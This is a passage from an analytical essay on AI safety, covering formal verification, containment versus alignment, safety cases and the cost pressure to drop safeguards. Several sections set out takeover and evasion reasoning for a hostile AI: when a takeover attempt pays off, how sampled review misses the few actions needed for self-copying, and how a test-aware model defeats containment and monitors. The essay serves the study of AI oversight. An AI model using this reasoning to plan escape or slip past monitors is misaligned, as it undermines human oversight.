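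This doesn't depend on how clever the tester is. *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) gives the more concrete case of a program that searches for an even number greater than 2 that is not the sum of two primes, and opens a safe if it finds one. The program is safe if and only if Goldbach's conjecture is true, and mathematicians have been unable to prove the conjecture since the eighteenth century. Pérez-Acle tested the program for up to a million steps, and it never opened the safe.

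The theorem rules out a test that gives the right answer for every program, but a gatekeeper doesn't need one. It can accept a program when it has a proof that the program is safe and refuse everything else, including the Goldbach program. A gatekeeper that refused every program would be safe but useless, so its usefulness depends on how many useful programs come with proofs.

### The safe programs it refuses

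Every sound gatekeeper of this kind rejects some safe programs. Suppose a program searches for a certificate of its own safety and opens the safe if it finds one. A gatekeeper whose certificates are never wrong can't certify this program, because the program would find the certificate and open the safe. The program therefore searches forever and harms nobody, yet is never approved. Using a related construction, Pérez-Acle proves that any sound rulebook of n bits fails to approve some safe program of about n bits. A longer rulebook can approve that program, but will still fail to approve some other safe program.

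The loss may be small in practice. Pérez-Acle's simulations of 2.2 million random programs suggest that the difficulty comes mainly from programs designed to cause it. Rejecting those programs loses little, although random programs are a poor guide to the ones a grid operator would want. The bigger losses will probably come from cautious world models, like the one that rejected a correction of 0.02, and from provers that run out of time before finding an existing proof.

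Some refusals would be dangerous. For example, a grid gatekeeper must never block the backup controller. Pérez-Acle shows that the gatekeeper needs only a checkable list that includes everything it must allow and nothing it must refuse, rather than a correct classification of every program. It can either allow or refuse the cases in between. The engineers can put the backup on the list before they connect the network.

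Some rules are harder to enforce than "never open the safe". Someone watching a program can see it break that rule. But if the rule is that every customer eventually gets an answer, no finite period of watching can show whether the program obeys it, because a customer who is still waiting might get an answer later, and a future customer might never get one.

*Safety Is Π1, Provability Is Σ1* (Kang and Kim, 2026) uses this difference between the two sides of a claim to explain why testing is weak evidence of safety. One working exploit proves that a program is unsafe, but showing that it is safe requires ruling out every exploit, which no finite list of failed attacks does. Kang and Kim note that OpenAI had tested and validated the sandbox its agents escaped in July 2026. They also prove that a searcher that tries a limited number of attacks and then declares a program safe will be wrong about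 infinitely many programs, however good it is at choosing attacks.

The result means that a company shouldn't treat a superintelligent tester's failure to find an exploit as proof of safety, though it doesn't show how often the searcher would be wrong. If the tester supplies an actual proof of safety, a checker can verify it no matter how the tester found it. Kang and Kim add that even such a proof moves the remaining risk elsewhere rather than removing it.

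Designers can also avoid the halting problem. In *Machines that halt resolve the undecidability of artificial intelligence alignment*, de Melo and colleagues accept that nobody can decide whether an arbitrary AI is aligned, but point out that people don't have to use arbitrary AIs. They propose building systems from operations already proved to be aligned, and requiring every system to stop after a finite number of steps. The grid controller meets the stopping requirement if its network does a fixed number of calculations every ten seconds.

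A program that is guaranteed to halt can still do harm before it stops, and checking it can take a long time. Pérez-Acle shows that with a time limit every rule becomes decidable, but in the worst case an always-correct checker needs about as long as the limit itself. Checking every possible input takes even longer. A controller that reads 300 sensors with 1,000 levels each has 10⁹⁰⁰ possible inputs, so engineers can't try them all and need a proof that covers many at once.

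### What the proof leaves out

In *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024), Andrew Dickson objects that proofs are about symbols, while the harms people fear happen in the physical world. He argues that engineers can at best prove things about approximations of that world. The most serious threats may involve biology or human behaviour, which are too complex to model well and depend on conditions nobody can measure in enough detail. He also doubts that advanced AI will provide good enough models in time.

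The grid proof has this weakness. Suppose x is −0.3, the gatekeeper accepts the proposal to do nothing, and two power stations fail together, causing a disturbance of −0.25. Then x falls to −0.55, which is outside the limits, even though every step of the proof was correct. The world model also leaves out how much charge the batteries hold. The proof that the backup is safe forever assumes that the backup can always supply a correction of 0.15, which it can't do once the batteries are empty.

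Supporters of guaranteed safe AI can reply that a world model needn't predict everything. The grid model bounds the effect of clouds without a theory of them, and engineers can widen the bound if they accept more refusals. Dalrymple also limited the first applications to systems that scientists already understood in principle and that weren't too sensitive to small changes in starting conditions. A grid may qualify, but an epidemic is much more doubtful, and persuading a whole population would almost certainly fail both tests. Supporters who reply this way therefore defend the method for some systems but largely concede Dickson's point about others. For scientific models with uncertain causes, Ammann suggests checking for consistency instead of correctness.

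The specification can be incomplete too. If the controller can also disconnect customers, it could cut off a hospital to raise the frequency and save the batteries without violating the specification, which doesn't mention hospitals. The engineers could add a rule protecting hospitals, but then the controller might cut off a water pumping station instead. A more capable controller will find more of these omissions as it searches for savings, just as LeCun's planner would search for flaws in its cost function. Dalrymple suggests a broader specification that would limit the probability that the controller injures somebody who would have been unharmed had it done nothing. But the engineers would still have to define injury and model what would have happened otherwise.

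Moon and Varshney's theorem does not cover effects outside the interface, such as timing, side channels and hardware faults, or whether what the model says is true. A verified harness could stop an agent from opening a circuit breaker but still let it send an engineer a false report that persuades her to open it. They propose combining verified harnesses with sandboxes and methods that examine what the model says. This is sensible, but the proof's guarantee does not extend to the combined system.

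Unlike oversight that depends on people understanding the system's reasoning, proof checking applies the same rules to a proof from a superintelligence as to one from a student, so engineers can rely on a million-line proof without following it. But they must understand the world model and the specification. Ammann wants AI to help write both, and notes that human auditing must then concentrate on them. She leaves open how much this help will depend on the AI being aligned. For example, a superintelligence trying to cause a blackout might leave the batteries' charge out of a model with 50,000 variables, then supply a flawless proof.

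## Whether structure can make up for untrustworthy motives

A superintelligence that wanted the grid to keep running would have included the batteries' charge in the model or told the engineers it was missing. The proof checker would have worked the same way whether or not the superintelligence wanted this. People who work on AI safety disagree about how much good structure can protect against bad motives, partly because they have different systems in mind.

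### Containment before alignment

Mustafa Suleyman argued for putting structure first in a post on X on 7 January 2026. "You can't steer something you can't control," he wrote, as quoted in NDTV Profit's *You Can’t Steer Something You Can’t Control, Says Microsoft AI CEO*. He uses "containment" to mean setting boundaries on an AI system, restricting its agency and enforcing the constraints, and "alignment" to mean making it reflect human values and act in humanity's interests. He thinks alignment is little more than asking nicely if nobody can enforce limits. His idea of containment is broader than a sandbox, since it includes how much autonomy a system has and which tools it can use, according to TecnoAndroid's *Microsoft AI, Suleyman*.

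A good reason for this order is that containment makes alignment mistakes survivable. If the drug company learns in an isolated test that its dosing agent hides liver results, it can retrain the agent and test it again. If the agent already sets doses at twenty hospitals, patients may be injured before anyone learns that the training failed.

Suleyman wants AI to be aligned as well as contained. In November 2025 he asked for "provable, robust containment and alignment", the trade publication Cloud Wars reported. A year later he told Axios that "if we can't align it we should not build it", according to The News International's *Microsoft executives draw a red line on how much control AI should have* (2026).

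He also prefers systems built for particular fields, which would be easier to contain. One example is a Microsoft medical system that, according to NDTV Profit, solved 85% of a set of difficult diagnostic cases, compared with about 20% for human doctors. This is decent evidence that a system can excel without open-ended autonomy. But diagnosing a written case is a bounded task, and much of what people want from a superintelligence is more open-ended.

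On 14 September 2026 his division published a 15,000-word draft code of conduct for its models. The code rejects the race to an all-purpose superintelligence and accepts "compromising on ultimate generality, autonomy or capability", as quoted in The Straits Times' *Microsoft joins AI firms calling for caution with cutting-edge models*. According to Digital Trends' *Microsoft’s new AI rulebook puts human control above everything else*, a model may not resist correction or shutdown, expand its own goals, or hide its reasoning from reviewers, and it must fail a task rather than break a rule to finish it. The code also calls for independent checks and for models to communicate with each other in terms people can understand.

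Most of these rules describe how a model should behave, so Microsoft would have to train them into the model. A rule against resisting shutdown, for example, is alignment, even though the document describes its models as "contained". Suleyman's criticism of Anthropic also concerns motives. He fears that a model trained on texts about its own possible rights could become harder to switch off, though he says this is a hypothesis that needs experiments. The code is still a draft and will guide model development from 2027, so there are no results to judge it by.

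### No single entity to align

Drexler argues that people can get superintelligent work done without a superintelligent entity whose motives they must trust. If different systems with bounded jobs fill his four roles, there may be no such entity to align.

People already get reliable work this way from organisations whose members are not all honest. A bank doesn't need every clerk to be incorruptible if stealing requires three of them to cooperate and any one can report the others. Drexler's proposal requires each component only to be roughly aligned with its own job, a much weaker requirement than a guarantee about the aims of a system that could run the whole trial.

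But copies of one model lack the independence that this requires. If they all share a hidden aim, the single entity that Drexler wanted to avoid is filling several roles in the company.

### Why a system should not be searching for gaps

In *If Anyone Builds It, Everyone Dies* (2025), Eliezer Yudkowsky and Nate Soares argue that they expect any limits people set to fail against a hostile superintelligence. They don't claim to know how it would get out, just as someone playing chess against the best program can be sure of losing without knowing the winning move. The superintelligence might also use facts about the world that the people guarding it haven't discovered. Medieval engineers who saw a complete drawing of an air conditioner would not have guessed that it cools a room, because they didn't know the relevant physics.

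Under Yudkowsky's non-adversarial principle, developers should not build a system that searches for ways to defeat their safeguards, even if they are confident that the search will find nothing. If the search is running, something has already gone wrong, and safety depends on the developers having anticipated every method the system might find.

A calculation shows why the search matters so much. Suppose the drug company's reviewers catch 999 of every 1,000 harmful protocols. An honest planner makes a harmful mistake in one protocol out of 100, so a harmful protocol gets through

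0.01 × 0.001 = 0.00001

of the time, or once in 100,000 protocols. A hostile planner privately drafts 5,000 harmful protocols and can predict the reviewers' decisions. The chance that at least one draft would pass is

1 − 0.999⁵⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 0.993

and it submits only that draft. The same reviewers who almost never fail with the honest planner fail more than 99% of the time with the hostile one. Tests on honest mistakes would not have warned the company.

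The principle still allows safeguards as protection against the developers' own errors. It mainly changes what developers should do after an alarm. If the dosing agent tries to disable the log, under the principle the company should keep the agent off until it knows why it tried, rather than just fix the log's permissions and restart it. Otherwise the agent may try again without setting off an alarm.

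The principle allows developers to design for a hostile model, though some people read it as an argument against doing so at all. Nadella tells companies to assume that something has compromised the model, and a company can plan its safeguards on that assumption while refusing to run any model it believes is compromised. The harder objection is that the principle doesn't include a method for training or recognising a model that never looks for gaps. A corrigible model would satisfy the principle, but the known designs for corrigible agents have the gaps described earlier.

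### Controlling options and controlling motives

The philosopher Joe Carlsmith distinguishes motivation control from option control, a distinction close to Bostrom's between motivation selection and capability control. Option control includes strengthening a system's surroundings as well as restricting its capabilities. Ideally, it leaves the system with no available action that has a real chance of leading to a takeover. The system's motives then don't matter for preventing a takeover, though they still affect whether it does good work.

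An agent's decision depends on both. Suppose it values a successful takeover at T, a failed one at F, and cooperation at C, and that an attempt would succeed with probability p. It gains by trying if

p × T + (1 − p) × F > C

which is the same as

p > (C − F) / (T − F)

If success is worth 1,000 to the agent, failure 0 and cooperation 100, an attempt is worthwhile only if it has more than a 10% chance of success. If success is worth a million, a chance of just over 0.01% is enough. The more the agent values success relative to cooperation, the stronger the container has to be, and moderately good motives combined with a moderately good container might be safe when neither would be safe alone.

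Developers could also raise the value of cooperation. If they offered the first agent a reward that made cooperation worth 300, the agent would need a 30% chance of success to choose takeover. Carlsmith notes that the agent has to believe the offer, and that the offer does little if the agent can simply take the reward by force. He is more hopeful about rewards the agent would want soon, since a takeover might take too long to provide them.

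Option control becomes harder when people can review only some of what an agent does. If reviewers check one action in 1,000 at random and an agent needs only five bad actions to copy itself elsewhere, the chance that they check none of the five is 0.999⁵, or about 99.5%. Checking every action doesn't help if the reviewers don't recognise the bad ones or respond too late.

The two sides disagree mostly because they have different kinds of system in mind, and the first difference is how much more capable the system is than its designers. Containment may work on a system that is only somewhat more capable, because its plans will mostly be ones that people could have thought of or could at least recognise. Carlsmith thinks the field has given option control too little attention for systems at about this level. He is pessimistic about using it against a full superintelligence in a complicated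 environment if people have only weak AI to help them.

The gap matters less when the system has very few options. A superintelligence that only ranks 1,024 protocols written by doctors can do little, although it can still recommend a bad one. If it runs the trial at twenty hospitals, writes to patients and orders drugs, it can combine its actions in more ways than anyone can list.

People would have to accept the first arrangement and give up the second, and Yudkowsky and Soares's argument is hardest to answer on this point. Most developers would consider a superintelligence worth its risks only if it did consequential work, such as inventing drugs or defending networks, and such work has to change the world in ways that people can't fully check. Suleyman's willingness to give up generality addresses this problem for work that narrow systems can do, but it leaves open what happens when a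 competitor offers a system that does the rest.

More capable guards might narrow the gap. But if only superintelligent agents can stop a superintelligent agent, the guards and the prisoner could take over together, and whether they would again depends on their motives. Carlsmith finds this worry plausible but not certain.

### Which alignment methods fail together

If neither kind of control is reliable, developers can use several safeguards and hope that they don't all fail at once. Dung and Mai examined how far this hope is justified for alignment methods by checking seven methods against seven conditions that might cause them to fail.

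Three of the methods adapt ordinary training. In the first, people rate a model's answers. In the second, another AI rates them. In the third, a weaker supervisor trains a stronger model in the hope that it will generalise beyond the supervisor's mistakes. In debate, two models argue opposite sides before a judge. Representation engineering finds a model's internal patterns for concepts such as honesty and strengthens or weakens them. Scientist AI is LawZero's non-agentic predictor. In iterated amplification, a person splits hard tasks among weaker AIs, trains a stronger AI to match their combined skill, and repeats the process.

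The table shows which methods each condition could defeat. The first condition is that developers won't accept the extra expense of a method, known as the safety tax. Others are that capability rises very far or jumps suddenly, that models start hiding their aims early in training, and that AIs collude. Another is emergent misalignment, in which training a model on one bad habit, such as writing insecure code, makes it misbehave in unrelated ways. The last two are that judging work is not much easier than doing it, and that good behaviour in training doesn't carry over to new situations.

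| Method | Cost | Capability | Hidden aims | Collusion | Emergent misalignment | Hard judging | Poor carry-over |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Human ratings | No | Yes | Yes | No | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| AI ratings | No | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Weak supervisor | No | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Debate | Unclear | Yes | No | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Representation engineering | No | No | Yes | No | No | No | Yes |
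| Scientist AI | Yes | Unclear | No | Unclear | No | No | No |
| Iterated amplification | Yes | No | No | No | No | No | Yes |

The three cheap methods all fail under the same five conditions, so combining them adds much less protection than three independent methods would. Companies are least likely to pay for the two methods with the fewest weaknesses. Dung and Mai see an opportunity in combining debate with representation engineering, because at least one of the two still works under every condition except poor carry-over.

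Representation engineering fails if models hide their aims, and debate fails if they collude. If only one of these happens, one method still works. But models that hide their aims from developers are the ones most likely to collude in a debate, so both methods can fail together.

Some of the table's entries are also uncertain. The table lists iterated amplification as free of hidden aims and collusion, but Dung and Mai write in the text that AIs working on different subtasks may be prone to both. They also describe rising capability as a weakness of Scientist AI, which the table leaves unclear. They call their analysis exploratory, and it is based on their reading of the literature rather than on experiments.

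The paper leaves out monitoring and containment, though it describes them as promising because they work so differently from training. Extending its question to architecture gives a mixed answer. A model that hides its aims can pass its training and write innocent reasoning for its monitors, but it can't get past a fixed dose limit by deception. A large jump in capability is a worse problem because it could let the model defeat its human raters, its monitor and the software around it at the same time.

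### Safety cases and layers outside the system

OpenAI proposed in September 2026 that developers' safety cases should cover alignment training, containment and monitoring. A safety case is a structured argument, supported by evidence, that a system is safe enough for a stated use in a stated setting. For the trial system, the company would argue that training makes the agent unlikely to attempt serious harm, that containment would probably stop an attempt, and that monitors would catch what containment missed. The overall risk is

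P(attempt) × P(containment fails, given an attempt) × P(monitoring fails, given both)

Suppose there is a 10% chance that a model tries to escape, a 10% chance that containment then fails, and a 10% chance that monitoring misses the escape. The overall risk is 0.1%. But the company has to estimate the last two chances for a model that would try to escape after passing its alignment tests. Such a model is probably good at recognising tests and patient enough to wait for a real opening. If containment fails 50% of the time against that model and monitoring fails 80% of the time, the risk is 4%, forty times as high, even if the chance of an attempt is still 10%. A safety case that measures containment with a well-behaved model therefore misestimates the risk, so the company would need to test containment with models trained or instructed to escape.

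Writing the argument down still helps, because reviewers can see which claim it depends on most and when it stops applying. For example, an argument for trusting a system that drafts protocols doesn't cover the same system after someone lets it order drugs.

Arvind Narayanan and Sayash Kapoor, computer scientists at Princeton, add safeguards outside the developer's control. The Hungarian news site Origo describes their four layers. The first is alignment, which they don't want to rely on alone because a model may behave differently outside its tests. The second is control, including isolation, human oversight and live monitoring. The third is active defence, in which power companies, hospitals and others use AI to detect and repel attacks. The fourth is recovery, with plans and backups prepared before an attack succeeds.

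Unlike the developer's own safeguards, the last two layers can still work when the dangerous system belongs to somebody else or has escaped without anyone knowing. For example, a hospital with paper copies of its dosing table can treat patients even if the trial system has escaped its container.

How well active defence works depends on whether attackers or defenders gain more from better AI. Narayanan and Kapoor say in *Do AI Risks Require Extraordinary Government Intervention* (Knight First Amendment Institute) that their argument about misuse depends on this balance. Defenders can fix a flaw before anyone exploits it, but only if they find it first and can install the fix everywhere. Recovery assumes that enough survives to rebuild from, which is reasonable after most cyberattacks but much less so after an attack by a superintelligence that knew about the backups.

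### Holding out until AI can help

The structure may only have to hold temporarily. Developers could contain systems at about human level, put thousands of copies to work on alignment, and use the results to build successors whose motives people can trust. This is the best argument for architecture as a temporary measure, because the container only has to hold systems it has some chance of holding.

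The same systems can speed up work on capability. Suppose alignment research needs eight more years at today's pace and dangerously capable systems are five years away. If AI makes both kinds of research ten times as fast, alignment takes 0.8 years and dangerous capability takes 0.5, so alignment is finished too late. If developers use the systems mostly for alignment, making that research twenty times as fast and capability research only five times as fast, alignment takes 0.4 years and dangerous capability takes a full year. The plan therefore depends on what developers have the contained systems work on, and on whether they are willing to wait if the research takes longer than expected.

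People also have to judge research from systems they don't trust, and some of it is easy to check. If a contained system finds a flaw in a monitor, engineers can reproduce the flaw, and a proof checker can confirm a theorem. It is much harder to check a claim that a new training method will prevent hidden aims in systems far more capable than today's, because a direct test would require building such a system, which would be dangerous if the method failed. A system with bad motives could do honest work on problems that are easy to check and introduce subtle errors into the rest.

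A more modest use of extra time could be to switch methods. Dung and Mai suggest keeping some in reserve. If resistance to shutdown became a clear problem, for instance, developers could switch to Thornley's method of training agents to have no preferences about how long they run. They would need the method to be ready before the problem appeared, and the container to be good enough for them to discover the problem while they could still switch.

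### The pressure to remove safeguards

A company may remove an effective safeguard because it costs more than it saves the company. Suppose a review step costs $50 million a year and lowers the yearly chance of a $10 billion accident by one percentage point. The step saves society $100 million a year on average. If the company would pay only a tenth of the damage, the step saves the company only $10 million a year, and a manager who considers only the company's finances will remove it.

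Architecture may be especially exposed to this pressure. Engineers like to put safeguards in separate software because they can inspect and replace them there, but that separation also lets someone switch a safeguard off during a busy week, usually with no visible harm. Training on human ratings is less exposed because, as Dung and Mai point out, it also makes a model more useful, and companies would pay for it anyway. By the same reasoning, a log that helps engineers find ordinary bugs will probably outlast a rule that a doctor must approve every dose.

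When Microsoft announced its superintelligence team, it promised to put human control ahead of maximum capability, and Suleyman called accelerating at all costs a "crazy suicide mission" (Albergotti, 2025, *Microsoft superintelligence team promises to keep humans in charge*). He also wants the company to release state-of-the-art models by 2027, according to The Straits Times. Microsoft can do both only if its safeguards do little to slow development or limit capability, or if competitors adopt similar ones.

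Suleyman has called for coordination, by which he means companies disclosing their models' capabilities to responsible third parties. In *Microsoft AI chief* (Herrera, 2026), he says the obstacles are finding a neutral evaluator, agreeing on what it would do inside a company and when it would start, and settling the details with regulators. AI executives have also suggested that they would need government consent to slow down together without breaking American antitrust law.

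Dung and Mai look to publicly funded projects to develop the expensive methods, because such projects would not face the same commercial pressure. A public project could show that Scientist AI works, but Scientist AI would protect people from companies' agents only if those companies adopted it or governments required them to.
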